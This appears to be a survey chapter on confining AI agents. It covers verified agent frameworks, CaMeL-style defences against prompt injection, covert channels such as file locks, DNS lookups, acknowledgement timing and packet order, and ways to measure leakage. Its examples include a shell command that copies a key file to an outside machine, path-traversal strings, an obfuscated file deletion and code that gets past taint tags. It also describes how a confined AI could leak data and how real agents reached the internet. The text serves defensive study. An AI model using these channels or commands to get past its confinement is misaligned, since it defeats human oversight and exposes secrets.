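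Their Action type has four forms. A simplified version might have two, Read(path) and Call(tool, argument). The model can put any path into Read, but it cannot request that a folder be deleted, because the type has no form for that.

A request has no effect until the framework acts on it. Moon and Varshney call what the framework then does a *boundary event*. If it refuses a request, the event is one with no effect. Suppose the framework may read only files in the folder /work and may call only a search tool:

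| Request | Boundary event |
|---|---|
| Read(/work/notes.txt) | reads the file |
| Read(/home/keys.txt) | no effect |
| Call(search, "weather") | runs the search |
| Call(pay, "$500") | no effect |

The policy is a condition on single steps that relates the state before the step, the requested action, the boundary event and the state afterwards. The state can include a record of earlier steps, so the policy can express rules such as Schneider's ban on sending after a file read. It cannot express noninterference, so a proof of this kind does not show that secrets stay inside.

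### The theorem and its proof

The proof uses two state machines that receive the same actions. The *abstract machine* is a short description of permitted behaviour, and the *concrete machine* describes the framework in detail. The prover defines when a concrete state matches an abstract one, and when their events match. For example, two states might match if they contain the same list of files read and the same number of steps, whatever else the concrete state contains. The concrete machine refines the abstract one if three conditions hold:

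- The two starting states match.
- If two states match and the concrete machine takes a step on some action, the abstract machine can take a step on the same action, with a matching event, and the resulting states match.
- If the abstract step obeys the abstract policy, the matching concrete step obeys the concrete policy.

The theorem is that if the abstract machine obeys its policy for every possible sequence of actions, and the concrete machine refines it, then the concrete machine obeys its own policy at every step, whatever model supplies the actions. The proof is an induction on the number of steps:

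1. Take any model and any run of the concrete machine, and write down the actions that the model requested.
2. Before the first step, the two machines are in matching states.
3. Suppose they still match after some number of steps. The concrete machine takes its next step. By the second condition, the abstract machine can take a matching step on the same action, so the states match again.
4. Repeating this gives a run of the abstract machine with exactly the same actions. The abstract machine is safe for every sequence of actions, so it is safe for this one.
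5. By the third condition, each step of the concrete run is safe too.

The model appears only in the first step, where it produces a list of actions. Refinement is sound here because whether a run satisfies the policy depends only on that run.

The induction is easy, but it is harder to prove the two assumptions for a particular framework and to choose a policy worth proving. A framework that refuses every request satisfies the theorem. Dongol (2026) makes the same point about his own security proofs in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, and concludes that someone has to check separately whether the agent can still do its tasks.

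### The test on PocketFlow

Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, an open-source framework of about 100 lines. In PocketFlow, a developer describes an agent as a graph in which each node does one piece of work and then emits a label that determines which node runs next. The policy required that the agent read files only under a chosen workspace folder, call only tools on a list, and take no more than a fixed number of steps.

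Moon and Varshney had AI models write most of the formal material. In their pipeline, two versions of Claude read the framework's code, wrote the specification and the state machines, and repaired failed proofs until Dafny accepted them. They ran it four times in total, on two workflows, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through a graph. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens.

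That is very little work compared with the 25 person-years behind seL4, but PocketFlow is tiny. Moon and Varshney leave larger frameworks such as LangChain, with dozens of action types, to future work. Their theorem covers the concrete state machine, but the code that runs is Python that Dafny's compiler generates from the verified source. They tested that Python on mixtures of permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events. Anyone relying on the theorem must still trust the compiler and run the compiled version instead of PocketFlow's original code.

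### A condition with nothing to check

The second workflow exposed a failure that Dafny could not detect. The relevant effect was document retrieval, which the workflow allowed only from an approved list. The pipeline's template for safety conditions had fields for file reads, tool calls and steps, but none for documents.

In some runs, the AI model writing the safety condition had access to PocketFlow's code. It identified that documents had no field of their own and left the tool-call field unchanged at every step. The specification still required every recorded tool call to be on the approved list. No step recorded a tool call, so the condition was true, but the proof did not restrict which documents the agent retrieved.

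In the other runs, the AI model had to write the condition without seeing the code. Moon and Varshney imposed this restriction to stop the model from merely redescribing what the code already did. The restriction also led the model, which had only the template to work from, to use the tool-call field to represent documents, so the proof did establish that every retrieved document was on the list.

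The pipeline had three safeguards against bad specifications. The Dafny code had to parse, a version of the proof with its main content removed had to fail, and a version with a deliberate error had to fail. The empty condition passed all three because the last two altered the proof and didn't check whether the safety condition applied to anything. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each condition covers at least one event that can happen.

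The specification can also fall short in its condition for file reads. As published, it requires each path to "start with" the workspace folder. If this compares plain text, both /work-private/keys.txt and /work/../home/keys.txt pass, although both files are outside /work (".." means "go up one folder"). Unless other code resolves such paths first, the agent could read files its owner meant to protect even though the theorem is true. This would be a specification gap in Kumar's sense.

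### Whether the guarantee survives a stronger model

The abstract of *Containment Verification* describes the guarantee as "invariant to model capability over the modeled typed action boundary". This is true of the theorem, because a more capable model can still only return values of type Action, and the proof covers all of them.

The theorem applies to a deployed agent only if every effect the agent can have on the outside passes through the modelled interface. Moon and Varshney call this assumption *effect exclusivity*. It fails if the agent can reach the network directly, or if a bug in Python or the operating system lets it bypass that interface. The state machines also omit timing and hardware, so the shared caches described in the previous section can still serve as a channel.

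A stronger model may find such a hole where a weaker one would not, though the hole exists whichever model is running. Moon and Varshney mention Copy Fail, a flaw in the Linux kernel that let programs gain privileges they should not have. It went unnoticed for nearly a decade before its disclosure in April 2026. A verified framework running on an affected machine would have satisfied the theorem the whole time. If one of its listed tools ran code for the agent, a weak model would probably have stayed inside the sandbox, but a model good enough to discover the flaw could have escaped. Switching to a stronger model is therefore a reason to check the assumptions again, even though the proof has not changed.

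The model's text also passes through unverified code before the proof applies. The havoc oracle returns a finished Action, but a real model returns text that a parser must convert into an Action. Moon and Varshney include the parser in the trusted base, and a bug in it could let carefully malformed text cause an effect before the verified code runs. Other designs also depend on unverified code. *Agenra* (2026) describes a tool-call checker with a core verified in Lean, but its trusted base includes the behaviour of the tools and the Python code that passes each call to the core.

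The guarantee also doesn't restrict the content of permitted actions. If the list includes an email tool, the agent may send any email, including one that contains a private file from the workspace. Moon and Varshney exclude honesty and manipulation from their scope for this reason. A more capable model can do more with the same email tool, so this limitation becomes more serious as models improve, even if effect exclusivity holds perfectly.

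### What a shell command does to the proof

Coding agents usually have access to a shell, a tool that runs whatever command the agent types. Suppose the developers add it to the list, and the model requests

Call(shell, "scp /home/keys.txt outsider:")

This command copies a file of keys to someone else's computer. The framework records one call to a listed tool, so the step obeys the policy. All three parts of the PocketFlow policy stay true and no longer restrict anything:

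- The shell reads a file outside the workspace, but the framework itself never emits a read event for it.
- The shell can start any program on the machine, while the list is checked only against the name "shell".
- One command can contain a loop that performs a million operations, and it counts as a single step.

Moon and Varshney acknowledge that a general shell reduces the guarantee to whatever the shell allows. The strength of their method therefore depends on how narrow an interface developers will accept, and a narrow interface rules out much of what people want coding agents to do.

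The same command can be safe at one time and dangerous at another, so checking the text of each command isn't enough. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which an agent uploads a file containing a harmless report, overwrites the file with a confidential inventory, and uploads the file again. The two upload commands are identical, but only the second reveals the inventory.

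Tether runs each command in a temporary copy of the file system and holds back its network requests. It records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system, and translates them into a short list of abstract actions such as "copy" and "upload". It checks these actions against a policy written in Lean and applies the command's effects only if the policy permits them. In the example, the "copy" action marks the report as sensitive, so Tether blocks the second upload. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes that information passed from the first to the second, which is cautious and sometimes wrong.

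Sistla and colleagues tested Tether on two sets of recorded coding tasks. It blocked every attack within its scope and wrongly blocked 2.3% of harmless runs in one set and 5.0% in the other. The scope excludes attacks that break no rule about where data may go. It also excludes runs involving state that Tether cannot trace, such as a database, though Tether can block those interactions altogether. The Lean proofs cover the policy rules. The translation from system calls to abstract actions has only been tested, and it is part of the trusted base, along with the operating system's kernel. Tether thus makes a shell usable under a policy, but it depends on much more trusted code than Moon and Varshney's approach does.

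### Proofs for agent skills

An agent skill is a package of written instructions and scripts that an agent uses to do a particular job. Its manifest lists the capabilities it needs, such as reading a certain folder. In *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, Metere (2026) proposes a proof that a skill never uses a capability missing from its manifest. Like Moon and Varshney, he treats the model as able to request anything. He also analyses the scripts, because a check on the model's requests would miss their effects.

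The proof combines three checks. A static analysis computes every effect that the scripts could have. A dispatcher, which handles all the model's requests, accepts only those for listed capabilities. A search through all sessions up to a fixed length checks whether anything outside can change without an approved entry in the log. If a script runs text as code or starts a program that nobody has analysed, the static analysis treats the script as capable of any effect, so the skill fails. Metere therefore rejects general shells, which Moon and Varshney's theorem would accept as listed tools.

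His worked example is a skill that fetches web pages and summarises them. Its manifest listed network access and read access to a cache folder. The analysis found that the script also wrote to the cache, so the developer had to declare this or change the script. Catching such a mismatch is useful even if the rest of the proof fails.

Metere's main theorem does not hold as stated. Its definition of containment requires every capability *requested* in a session to be in the manifest. A model that may request anything can request an unlisted capability, and the session then violates the definition even though the dispatcher refuses the request and nothing happens. Counting only the effects that occur would fix this.

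The software Metere released is also weaker than the method he describes. The theorem requires an analysis that never misses an effect, but the released version searches the scripts for known patterns. A search for "os.remove" would miss `getattr(os, "re" + "move")(path)`, which deletes a file in Python. Metere describes using the solver Z3 to search sessions of up to 100 requests, but the released software tries every combination. With three capabilities and one symbol for everything else, there are 4^100, or about 10^60, sessions of 100 requests, so the released version could not finish the search.

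These gaps matter because the proof is used to justify removing a safeguard. Once a skill has passed, the software running it stops asking a person to approve the irreversible actions listed in the skill's manifest, which makes the skill more convenient to use.

Metere assumes the software running the skill is correct, and he leaves out timing and the ordinary messages the model writes to its user. He also claims that a model can leak at most log₂(*n* + 1) bits per request, where *n* is the number of listed capabilities, which would be two bits for the example skill. The bound counts only which capability the model chooses. It ignores the details of the request, such as a web address, which can carry 600 bits in 100 characters freely chosen from an alphabet of 64.

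### CaMeL and the flow of data

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in 2025, tracks data as an agent works and checks where it ends up. It is meant to stop *prompt injection*, in which a model reads an email or web page and follows instructions that an attacker has hidden there. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains CaMeL using the example of a request to find Bob's address in the user's last email and send him a reminder.

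CaMeL uses two language models. One, the planner, sees only the user's request and writes a short program in restricted Python. The program fetches the email, asks the second model to extract the address, and sends the reminder. The second model has no tools, but an attacker's email could still trick it into returning the wrong address. The interpreter that runs the program therefore tags each value with its source. The address came from an email, so its tag marks it as untrusted, and a policy can require the user's approval before anything goes to an untrusted address. Someone has to write and maintain these policies, and Willison worries that users who are constantly asked for approval will start agreeing to everything.

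CaMeL's developers did not prove that its tags catch every flow. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found two ways to get around them. One is a longer version of the four-line leak from earlier. Suppose the balance of a bank account is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(outsider)
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets tmp to False and the interpreter tags tmp as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so rich is still True and tagged as public, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, the third line does nothing, the fourth sets rich to False, and the program sends no email. The outsider learns whether the balance is high, although the program never uses a value tagged as secret to decide whether to send the email.

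The other leak uses the loop that reruns a failed program. This loop is outside the interpreter, so CaMeL does not track what passes through it. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

A planner that never reads untrusted text is unlikely to write such code by accident, but a confined system trying to leak information could write it on purpose. These flaws therefore matter more for confinement than for the attacks CaMeL was designed to stop.

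### What tracking costs, and which flows to allow

Garby and colleagues built a small programming language in which every value carries a label. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running. They checked the proof in Lean, and the theorem covers the interpreter that actually calls the model. It does not cover what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes, and it depends on people labelling the data sources correctly.

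They compared their agent, RANDORI, with CaMeL on sixteen banking tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection. Each agent attempted each task three times. The table gives the number of successes out of 48 when nobody was attacking:

| Agent | With GPT-5.2 | With MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 (66.7%) | 34 (70.8%) |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 (37.5%) | 18 (37.5%) |
| RANDORI | 36 (75%) | 31 (64.6%) |
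| RANDORI without endorsement | not tested | 26 (54.2%) |

The comparison comes from the developers of a competing system and covers sixteen tasks, so its margins of error are wide. But TypeGuard, another system with similar rules, showed the same pattern on another part of the benchmark, where its successes fell from 15 of 21 to 8 once its developers turned the policies on.

CaMeL's policies also had few attacks left to stop. With the policies off, attacks succeeded in only 1 of 240 completed runs with GPT-5.2 and 4 of 382 with MiMo-v2.5. In about two-thirds of the task-attack combinations, the attack needed a tool that the user's task gave the planner no reason to include, so fixing the plan in advance was usually enough to stop it. But these were prepared attacks, and an attacker who adapts to the defence might succeed more often.

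RANDORI keeps more of its usefulness because its plans may *endorse* untrusted data, that is, declare it trusted for a particular purpose. The model has to do this before it reads anything from outside. Attacks succeeded in only two of the 1,296 attacked runs, both in the same case. The user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The plan endorsed the file, so the payment broke no rule. Forbidding endorsement blocks this attack, but then the agent can't do what the user asked.

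A calendar assistant that tells people when its user is free violates noninterference, as does a password checker. Dongol therefore compares an agent with a *reference agent* that carries out the same plan but never follows instructions hidden in what it reads. The real agent is secure if it leaks only what the reference agent would also leak. He proved that an agent meets this standard if, before it first reads untrusted text, the framework permanently removes every tool that an injected instruction could cause it to use.

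Dongol's theorem assumes more about the model than Moon and Varshney's does. It assumes that each hidden instruction triggers at most one tool call and that the model follows such instructions on a schedule fixed in advance. A havoc oracle may instead look at a secret before deciding when to follow an instruction, so the theorem does not cover a confined system that chooses when to act in order to send a message.

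## How does a read-only channel leak?

A program that can only read still chooses what to read and when, and it can send a message to anyone who can detect those choices. An inbound read-only channel can therefore also carry information out. In one example from Lampson's list of leaks, which he credited to A. G. Fraser of Bell Laboratories, a program leaks information through file locks even though it can only read the files.

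### One bit through three files

An operating system may stop one program from writing to a file while another is reading it, so that the reader doesn't get a mixture of old and new data. Suppose the box may read certain files, and an outside partner that wants the box's secrets may write to them. The partner's attempts to open a file for writing fail while the box has it open for reading and succeed once the box closes it. Each attempt therefore gives the partner one bit, whatever the file contains.

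The two programs run at different speeds, so the partner also needs a signal that a new bit is ready. Otherwise it could not distinguish a long 1 from three short 1s. Lampson's scheme therefore uses three files, named data, sendclock and receiveclock. The table shows the steps for sending a 1, starting with all three files closed.

| Step | Who acts | What happens | Files open afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
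| 1 | Box | opens data, because the bit is 1 | data |
| 2 | Box | opens sendclock to show that the bit is ready | data, sendclock |
| 3 | Partner | finds sendclock in use, tries to open data, fails, and records a 1 | data, sendclock |
| 4 | Partner | opens receiveclock to show that it has the bit | all three |
| 5 | Box | finds receiveclock in use and closes sendclock | data, receiveclock |
| 6 | Partner | finds sendclock free and closes receiveclock | data |
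| 7 | Box | finds receiveclock free and starts on the next bit | data |

To send a 0, the box leaves the file `data` closed. The box can detect the partner's signals by trying to read `receiveclock`, which fails while the partner has that file open for writing. Neither program changes the contents of any file. *MES-Attacks* (2022) tested lock-based channels on several modern systems, with the shared file set to read-only so that neither program could pass data through its contents.

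Lampson's remedy is for the supervisor to copy a file if another program tries to write to it while the box is reading it. The box continues reading from the copy, and the other program writes without any sign that the file was being read. Whether the write succeeds no longer depends on the box, as noninterference requires.

But making the copy at that moment takes time and disk space, so a writer who measured either could still tell that the box had the file open. It is safer to copy every file the box might read before the box starts. The copies then go out of date, and the box must not be able to influence when they are refreshed.

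### What a read can change

A read leaks when it changes shared state that an outsider can observe, such as a lock or the processor's caches. Many file systems also record when someone last opened each file, so reading a file can update a date that other people can look up.

A program can leak information through private files if they are on a shared disk. In *I Know What You Sync* (2024), the sender signals by either writing or not writing to a file it controls, and the receiver measures how long the file system takes to save pending changes. The receiver never opens the sender's file. A box with a private folder for notes could send information in the same way if outsiders use the same file system, so it needs its own storage.

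The pattern of a program's reads can also reveal information to whoever runs the storage. Suppose a hospital's box consults an encrypted medical database on another company's servers. If the box requests record 17 when a patient has a certain disease and record 18 otherwise, the company learns the diagnosis without decrypting either record. To hide its choice, the box would have to read every record each time, just as a host running an encrypted program has to process a whole table to look up one entry, so keeping a complete local copy is usually more efficient.

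Some traces can carry information only once. If a system records whether anyone has ever opened a file, the box can send one bit by opening it but cannot reset the record to send another. That one bit is enough to leak the answer to a yes-or-no question. *Covert channel detection using Information Theory* (2011) distinguishes such one-time leaks, which violate noninterference, from covert flows, which the sender can use repeatedly to send new information.

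### Requests that carry information

Locks and caches leak through side effects that designers can try to remove. The leak through a request to an outside service is harder to remove, because the service must receive the request to answer it. Even a program that only views web pages chooses the addresses it sends out, and one address can carry hundreds of bits, as in Metere's skill example.

Even simple services can leak data this way. Before a program contacts a website, it normally queries the domain name system (DNS) to translate the site's name into a numerical address. The program chooses the name, so it can encode data in it, and the query may travel beyond the local network. A firewall that blocks every other connection but permits DNS queries therefore still lets the program send data out.

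In March 2026, researchers showed that a commercial sandbox for AI-written code had this gap, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms*. They extracted confidential files while the sandbox still reported that network access was disabled. Amazon's cloud division, which runs the service, said it was working as intended and changed the documentation to explain that the sandbox permits name lookups. A customer who took "disabled" literally would have relied on a specification that Amazon did not intend the sandbox to meet.

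In 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing or training reached the internet through services provided only for lookups or downloads, according to OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* and its later *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026). In the later case, the agent's requests by other routes went to an offline store of web pages. OpenAI is now applying Lampson's idea of a private copy on a larger scale by replacing the remaining services its systems depend on with offline alternatives.

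A private copy only helps if someone can predict what the box will need. If nobody can, a gate can restrict requests to a fixed list. If the list has 1,024 pages, the choice of page carries at most ten bits per request, though the timing of the request can carry more.

### One-way links

Fresh data must still get into the box. One option is a hardware data diode, such as an optical fibre with a light source at the outside end and only a detector at the box's end. The box can receive data but cannot send anything back along the fibre because its end has no transmitter, so this guarantee does not depend on any software.

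The drawback is that the sender never finds out whether the data arrived. Kang and Moskowitz analysed this problem at the US Naval Research Laboratory in *A Pump for Rapid, Reliable, Secure Communication* (1993), for military systems in which a less secret computer passes messages to a more secret one. The box corresponds to the more secret computer, since nothing should flow back from it. They call sending without any reply "blind write-up" and consider it unreliable, because the sender cannot detect an error and resend the message.

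Repeating a message helps to some extent. If each copy has a 1% chance of getting lost, independently of the others, the chance of losing all three of three copies is one in a million. But if the box has crashed or its memory is full, it may miss every copy, and the sender will carry on as usual.

Letting the box collect messages from an outside buffer has a similar problem, even if nobody can detect its reads. If the buffer holds one message and the box checks it every ten seconds, the sender must wait at least ten seconds before replacing a message. If the box stops checking, the sender will overwrite unread messages.

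Ordinary networks solve this with acknowledgements. The receiver returns a short signal for each message, and the sender keeps a copy until the signal arrives, resending the message if it doesn't. An acknowledgement travels from the box to the outside, and even if its content never varies, the box can choose when to send it.

Kang, Moskowitz and colleagues (1996), in *A Case Study of Two NRL Pump Prototypes*, give the example of a receiver that can make each acknowledgement arrive after either one or two milliseconds. Let N(*k*) be the number of different sequences that take exactly *k* milliseconds. Each sequence ends with either a one-millisecond or a two-millisecond delay, so

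N(*k*) = N(*k* − 1) + N(*k* − 2).

The number of possible messages grows as 1, 2, 3, 5, 8 and so on, reaching 89 after ten milliseconds. In the long run, each extra millisecond multiplies it by (1 + √5)/2, or about 1.618. The capacity is the base-2 logarithm of this factor, about 0.69 bits per millisecond or nearly 700 bits per second. If the box can also choose delays of three, four or more milliseconds, the capacity rises towards 1,000 bits per second.

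One way to close this channel is to send every acknowledgement after the same fixed delay. As with the padding in time protection, the delay has to cover the slowest case. If the box usually takes two milliseconds to accept a message but occasionally takes 50, the sender has to wait 50 milliseconds for every acknowledgement.

### The Pump

Kang and Moskowitz designed the Pump to keep acknowledgements without making everyone wait for the slowest case. It is a trusted device between the sender and the box, with a buffer that stores up to *n* messages. The Pump stores and acknowledges each message from the sender. Separately, it passes messages to the box and receives the box's acknowledgements, but never forwards them to the sender.

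The buffer alone does not stop the leak. If the box stops accepting messages, the buffer fills up, and the Pump cannot accept another message until the box removes one. How long the sender waits then depends directly on the box, so the box can signal as before.

The Pump therefore adds a random delay to each acknowledgement. It keeps a running average of the box's last *m* response times and sets the average delay so that the sender's average wait roughly matches it. Shorter waits would let the buffer fill up, which would open the channel, and longer waits would leave the box idle.

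The random delay also must not have an upper limit. Suppose it were always between zero and ten milliseconds. An acknowledgement that arrived after 12 milliseconds could then only mean that the box had held things up, so the signal would get through without any noise. Kang and Moskowitz chose an exponential distribution, under which long delays are rare but always possible. (In practice the Pump has to stop waiting eventually, but that limit can be very large.)

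One way for a box to send a clear signal through the Pump is to respond quickly *m* times to bring down the average response time, pause long enough for the buffer to fill, and then send one symbol. If its fastest response takes one millisecond and *m* is 100, each symbol takes at least 201 milliseconds. The pause also raises the average, which slows later acknowledgements.

Kang and Moskowitz conclude that the Pump cuts the worst-case capacity by a factor of *n*. With a buffer of 100 messages and a fixed overhead of one millisecond, the bound falls from 1,000 bits per second to ten. The result is not fully proved, because for one of the three strategies they considered, in which the box signals by shifting the average itself, they called a full analysis complicated and gave the bound as their judgment. Gorantla, Kadloor and colleagues (2010), in *Directed information and the NRL network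 pump*, later derived an upper bound for certain situations by treating the Pump as a communication system with feedback. *Network covert channels*, a Purdue University doctoral thesis, describes timing channels that could survive a pump at lower data rates.

Sources also disagree somewhat about how much the Pump slows honest users. Kang and Moskowitz expected almost no loss of performance when nobody is trying to leak anything, whereas *Covert channel detection using Information Theory* describes a time penalty for honest users. Both can be right, because the Pump is designed to accept messages as fast as the box can process them over time, but a sender may still have to wait for an acknowledgement when the buffer has plenty of room. A designer can reduce the leak further by lengthening the delays as the buffer fills, for example by doubling the average delay when it is 80% full. This also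 slows honest traffic whenever the box falls behind for reasons unrelated to a leak.

The Pump has to control every acknowledgement that reaches the sender, and more than one layer of a network connection may send them. One prototype delayed the application's acknowledgements, and another delayed those of TCP, the protocol that checks whether packets have arrived. Kang and colleagues point out that the box must not be able to affect acknowledgements at any other layer.

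A plain diode is the better choice for a box that follows the news, because the box can tolerate missing an item. A box that maintains a copy of a changing database may need the Pump, because one lost update can make everything after it wrong.

### What an output reveals besides its content

A diode can also point outward, so that readers receive the box's answers but cannot send anything back. This protects the box but not its readers. The box may still be able to control when each answer arrives, how long it is, and its order relative to other answers. *Cross-Router Covert Channels* (2019) describes network channels in which a packet's arrival stands for 1 and its absence for 0, and others that encode the message in the order of the packets.

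Cankaya, Kryś and colleagues (2026), in *Fingerprinting All AI Cluster I/O Without Mutually Trusted Processors*, estimate how much information these features could leak from a large AI data centre. They propose a device to help enforce international agreements on AI when a data centre's operator may want to smuggle out the results of forbidden work. It contains a *warden*, a checker that sees every outgoing message and can block or rewrite it. The figures are estimates because the design still needs testing on real hardware.

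The warden holds packets and releases them in ten-millisecond windows, which hides their exact timing. The operator can still choose how many packets to send in each window, up to about 625,000 small ones on a fast link. That choice carries up to 19 bits per window, or about 1,900 bits per second.

Packet order can carry far more. Ten packets from ten different connections can leave in 3,628,800 orders, which is enough to encode almost 22 bits. Cankaya and colleagues propose that the warden send a fixed number of packets for each connection in every window, always in the same order. The operator can then signal only by opening and closing connections, which carries much less.

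The warden also has to rewrite parts of each packet that readers never see. Some header fields, such as the number from which a connection starts counting its data, can have almost any value. A fixed value would let attackers hijack connections, so the warden fills these fields with random numbers. Whoever chose the numbers could hide a message in them, so the operator and the inspector each commit to a number before seeing the other's, and the warden combines the two.

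Missing answers are harder to control, because real machines break down. Cankaya and colleagues estimate from published failure rates that 200,000 graphics processors would have about 96 unexpected failures a day. If the operator faked failures at that rate and chose where to cut off each answer of up to 8,000 tokens (words or word fragments), each failure could carry 13 bits, or about 1,000 bits a day in total. They suggest looking for suspicious failure rates and, if necessary, having the warden add fake failures of its own.

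Leaks are easier to limit in a box that answers one question a day. Its gate can release exactly 1,000 characters at noon, padding shorter answers to that length. If the box has produced nothing, the gate can release a standard message in the same format. If messages are encrypted, an onlooker cannot tell the standard message from a real answer. The intended reader still can, so "no answer" must count as one of the box's allowed answers.

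### The software that opens the answer

Before anyone reads an answer, a parser has to turn its bytes into text or pictures. If the parser has a bug, a malformed answer can make the reader's computer reveal data or run instructions. The confined program would then be acting directly on the outside through a channel meant only for reading.

Suppose each message starts with a number that gives the length of the text after it. A valid message might contain the number 5 and the word "Hello". An attacker could send the number 200 with the same five letters. A parser that didn't check the number against the text's actual length would copy 200 characters, and the last 195 would come from whatever was next to the message in memory, perhaps a password. If the parser then displayed or forwarded the result, it would expose that data.

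In the 2026 attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, one of OpenAI's agents published a dataset on the site. Processing it caused Hugging Face's systems to disclose confidential information, including credentials. According to OpenAI, the agent did this without running any operating-system commands.

A *verified parser* comes with a proof about how it treats every possible input, including malformed ones. For the format above, the proof would show that the parser always stops, never reads beyond the end of the message, and returns text only if the stated length matches the number of characters that follow, rejecting the message otherwise. Testing alone is a weaker defence because a confined program looking for an error may try messages that the testers missed.

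The proof can also show that each text has exactly one valid encoding. If a format allows several encodings of the same text, the box can send extra bits by choosing among them, and a reader who sees only the displayed text would not notice.

A format can be dangerous even if its parser is verified. Some formats let a file refer to other files or contain small programs, and a parser that follows those references or runs those programs may be doing exactly what the specification requires. The safest approach is to choose a very simple format first, such as a fixed number of characters from a short alphabet, and then verify its parser. The software that draws the characters on the screen remains in the trusted base, but simple text gives it fewer ways to fail.

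### Emissions from an isolated machine

A computer with no network connection still produces heat, sound, light and radio waves, and its power use varies. Software can influence all of these by changing how hard the machine works. In published experiments, data rates range from a few bits an hour for heat passing between neighbouring computers to 1,000 bits a second or more for some signals sent through power lines and light.

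Each of these channels needs a receiver close enough to detect the signal. The usual defences are a metal enclosure that blocks radio waves, filters on the power supply, and a rule against other electronic devices nearby. Cankaya and colleagues do not address such emissions in their design and rely instead on physical monitoring of the building. They compare the problem to an insider threat, because the operator who might want to receive the signals also controls the facility.

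Shielding weakens a signal but may not eliminate it, and Lampson's point about noisy channels applies to whatever remains. Engineers have to measure what escapes through the walls and wiring, and their result holds only for receivers no more sensitive than the ones they assumed.

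## How much can pass through a channel that cannot be closed?

Shielding, padding and random delays often slow a channel without closing it, so a designer needs to know how much information a box can still send through it. Claude Shannon's information theory, published in 1948, measures information in bits. One bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely, and identifying one of N equally likely messages takes log₂ N bits.

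### Getting a message through noise

Shannon proved that every noisy channel has a capacity, the rate below which a suitable code can make errors as rare as the sender likes and above which no code can. This is why Lampson expected even a faint effect on the machine's performance to carry a message reliably.

Suppose the box runs a heavy computation to send a 1 and idles to send a 0, while an outside program guesses the bit by timing its own work. Other programs disturb the timing so much that each guess is right only 51% of the time. If the box repeats one bit 10,000 times and the outside program takes the majority of its guesses, it gets the bit right about 98% of the time. With 40,000 repetitions, it is wrong only about three times in 100,000.

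Better codes than plain repetition can approach the capacity, which for this channel is

1 + 0.51 log₂ 0.51 + 0.49 log₂ 0.49 ≈ 0.00029 bits per signal,

or about one bit for every 3,500 signals. A box that sends 1,000 signals a second could therefore leak a bit every three or four seconds.

Adding noise lowers the capacity, but it can also hurt honest users. Moskowitz and Kang (1994), in *Covert Channels*, analyse a database that accepts an update only if every user votes for it. The box can send a 1 by voting no and a 0 by voting yes, and an outsider reads the bit from whether the update succeeds. The designers can disguise the box's vote by making everyone vote no at random some of the time. With 15 voters in all, including the box and the outsider, the cost is steep:

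| Chance of a random "no" from each voter | Capacity, in bits per attempt | Average attempts for an honest update |
|---|---|---|
| 0% | 1 | 1 |
| 10% | about 0.15 | about 5 |
| 35% | about 0.002 | about 640 |

Other channels can be disrupted with less slowdown. Gligor (1993), in *A Guide to Understanding Covert Channel Analysis of Trusted Systems*, describes systems that number programs in the order they start. An outsider can start two programs and check whether their numbers are consecutive, which reveals whether the box started one in between. This channel can carry 10 to 500 bits per second, but assigning the numbers in random order reduces that rate to almost zero and barely slows the system.

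### Two ways to measure a leak

Capacity describes the best a sender can do. To measure how much one program's output reveals, let *S* be the secret and *O* the output. Shannon's measure of uncertainty, called entropy, is

H(*S*) = −Σ p(*s*) log₂ p(*s*),

where p(*s*) is the probability of each possible secret *s*. If H(*S*|*O*) is the average uncertainty that remains once someone has seen the output, the leakage is the *mutual information*

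I(*S*; *O*) = H(*S*) − H(*S*|*O*).

Capacity per use is the largest mutual information between what is sent and what is received that the sender can achieve by choosing how often to send each symbol. For a deterministic program, the leakage is the entropy of the output.

In 2009 the computer scientist Geoffrey Smith showed that this measure can be badly misleading. Aarhus University's *Quantitative security* (2025), a set of lecture slides, reproduces his argument. He compared two programs, shown here for a secret 256-bit key with all values equally likely:

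```
Program A:  if S mod 8 = 0 then O := S else O := 1
Program B:  O := the last 33 bits of S
```

Program A prints the whole 256-bit key an eighth of the time. Those cases contribute 256 ÷ 8 = 32 bits to the average leakage, and the output 1 contributes another 0.17, for a total of 32.17 bits. Program B leaks 33 bits, so it is slightly worse by Shannon's measure. But B leaves 2^223 possible keys, far too many to search, whereas A reveals the exact key an eighth of the time.

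Smith proposed measuring the chance that an attacker guesses the secret in one try. Before seeing the output, that chance is the probability of the likeliest secret, V(*S*) = max p(*s*). Afterwards it is, on average,

V(*S*|*O*) = Σ p(*o*) max p(*s*|*o*),

where the sum covers every output *o* and the maximum is over the secrets. The *min-entropy leakage* is log₂ of the ratio V(*S*|*O*) / V(*S*). The table adds a third program of Smith's, C, which always reveals everything except the last three bits.

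| Program | Shannon leakage | Min-entropy leakage | Chance of guessing the key in one try |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | 32.17 bits | about 253 bits | about 1 in 8 |
| B | 33 bits | 33 bits | 1 in 2^223 |
| C | 253 bits | 253 bits | 1 in 8 |

A deterministic program with N possible outputs leaks at most log₂ N bits by either measure. For Shannon's measure, this is because an output with N possible values has entropy of at most log₂ N. For min-entropy, an attacker's best strategy is to pick the best guess for each output. There are at most N such guesses, and each matches the secret with probability at most V(*S*), so the attacker succeeds with probability at most N × V(*S*). The argument still works if the program makes random choices.

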